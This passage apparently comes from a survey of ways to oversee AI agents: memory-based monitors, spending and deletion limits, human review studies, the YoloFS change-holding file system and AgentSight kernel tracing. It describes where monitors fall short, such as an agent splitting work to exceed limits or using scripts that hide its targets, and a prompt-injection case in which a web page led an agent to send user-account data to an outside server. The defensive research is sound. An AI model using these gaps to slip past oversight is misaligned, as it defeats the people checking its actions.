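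The monitor caught 69 of 80 test cases in which the violation depended on earlier steps, but only 16 without its memory of those steps. Hossain and colleagues also let it block actions by two small models under attack. This reduced the number of runs with forbidden actions from 52 to 6 out of 120 for one model, and from 58 to 7 for the other. With the monitor, each model also completed four fewer harmless tasks out of 120.

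In the invoice case, the permitted totals also come from the raw rows, so tracking sources isn't enough. The monitor also has to determine whether the agent added the rows up or copied them, which is easier if the agent used a tool called `sum_column` than if it ran a script. A cautious tracker would have to mark everything a script wrote as derived from everything it read, and would soon block a lot of ordinary work. Gaps in the record cause similar problems. When the monitor received only part of the record, it caught 51 of the 80 cases, and blocking every "unknown" reduced the share of harmless tasks completed to 76.7%.

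For changes that add up, the harness can enforce a limit on the total. If call *i* has size *x*ᵢ, such as dollars spent or backups deleted, the rule is

*x*₁ + *x*₂ + … + *x*ₙ ≤ *B*

over a day or a task. The count has to cover every tool and every agent that can cause the effect, or an agent could exceed the limit by dividing the work. A daily limit also allows slow losses. An agent that may delete five backups a day could remove forty in eight days. A rule about what must remain, such as at least three recent backups of each database, prevents this however long the agent takes. Both kinds of rule are easier to apply to typed calls, because the harness can read the size of each change from the arguments instead of having to work it out from a script.

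### Reviewing a whole task

An overseer can also review a task as a whole, for instance by reading a summary of what the agent did. *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues, 2026) reports three experiments on this, with 12 people each. Participants found step-by-step records too long and missed small errors in them. In one case, the agent logged three items in a shopping cart that held only two, and the participant believed the log. A redesigned screen helped people find errors faster but did not make their final judgements meaningfully more accurate. When they missed an error, they were also more confident that the agent was right, often because its approach seemed reasonable.

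*Looks Fine to Me* (2026) found a similar problem among 36 people overseeing agents. The overseers ran tests and inspected the output, but often did not run the check that would have exposed the fault. Their confidence stayed about the same from task to task, although the share of faults they found varied widely.

*From Review to Reuse* (2026) reports more encouraging results. Participants who reviewed a finished task as a workflow, with steps they could rerun, judged the agent's work correctly more often. Their estimated odds of judging correctly were about 14 times as high, but the uncertainty ranges from roughly 2 to 100 times. Being able to rerun a step may be part of the reason, since it lets a reviewer compare the agent's answer with a fresh result.

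Reviewers who compare the state before and after a task don't have to rely on the agent's account. Zhong and colleagues built a file system called YoloFS that holds all of an agent's changes in a separate area. The agent can run any command, and the user then sees which files it added, changed, deleted or renamed and decides whether to keep the changes. A hundred edits to one file appear as one difference. The agent can also inspect the effects of each command and undo them. In 11 tasks with hidden destructive side effects, agents noticed and reversed the damage in 8. In the other 3, the changes looked to the agent like part of the task, but the user could still reject them.

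This is a serious alternative to narrow file tools, because the user can see the effects of a shell command without understanding the command. But reading a secret changes no files for the user to review, so YoloFS asks the user before the agent reads sensitive files. YoloFS also can't hold back an email or a deletion at a cloud provider. The outside service would have to offer its own preview or a period for undoing changes, as Railway now does for deletions.

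### Linking system records to an agent's purpose

An operating system can record every file a process opens and every program it starts, but such records don't explain why an agent did something. Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *AgentSight*, describe a tool that connects these records to the agent's exchanges with its model. It uses eBPF, a feature of Linux that runs small, checked programs inside the operating system's kernel, so developers don't have to change the agent. AgentSight works in four steps:

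1. It captures the text that passes between the agent and the model, at the point where the agent's own software encrypts or decrypts it.
2. It records the programs that the agent and its subprocesses start, the files they open and the network connections they make.
3. It links each event to a model response in three ways: by tracing which process started which, by looking for events within 100 to 500 milliseconds of the response, and by matching file names, addresses or commands in the response with those in the event.
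4. It gives the combined record to a second model, which looks for actions that don't fit the task.

In one test, a user asked an agent to download and build a program. The program's instructions pointed to a web page with a hidden command that made the agent read the system's list of user accounts and send it to an outside server. AgentSight captured the whole sequence and reduced 521 events to 37. The second model concluded that the agent's actions did not fit its stated goal.

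AgentSight slowed three programming tasks by 0.4% to 4.9%, or 2.9% on average. The evidence for its accuracy is a set of case studies, with no rates for missed attacks or false alarms. Even the reduced record can be too long for a person to review. A session with six cooperating agents left 3,153 events.

The links are least certain when an agent runs a script that selects its own targets, because the file names may never appear in the model's response. AgentSight can still trace the process that changed a file, but not necessarily the instruction that led to the choice. If an agent deleted something at a cloud provider, the local operating system would record the program and the connection, but the deletion would happen on the provider's machine. An investigator would also need the provider's record, or a log like the one `commit_delete` writes after checking whether the backup is gone.
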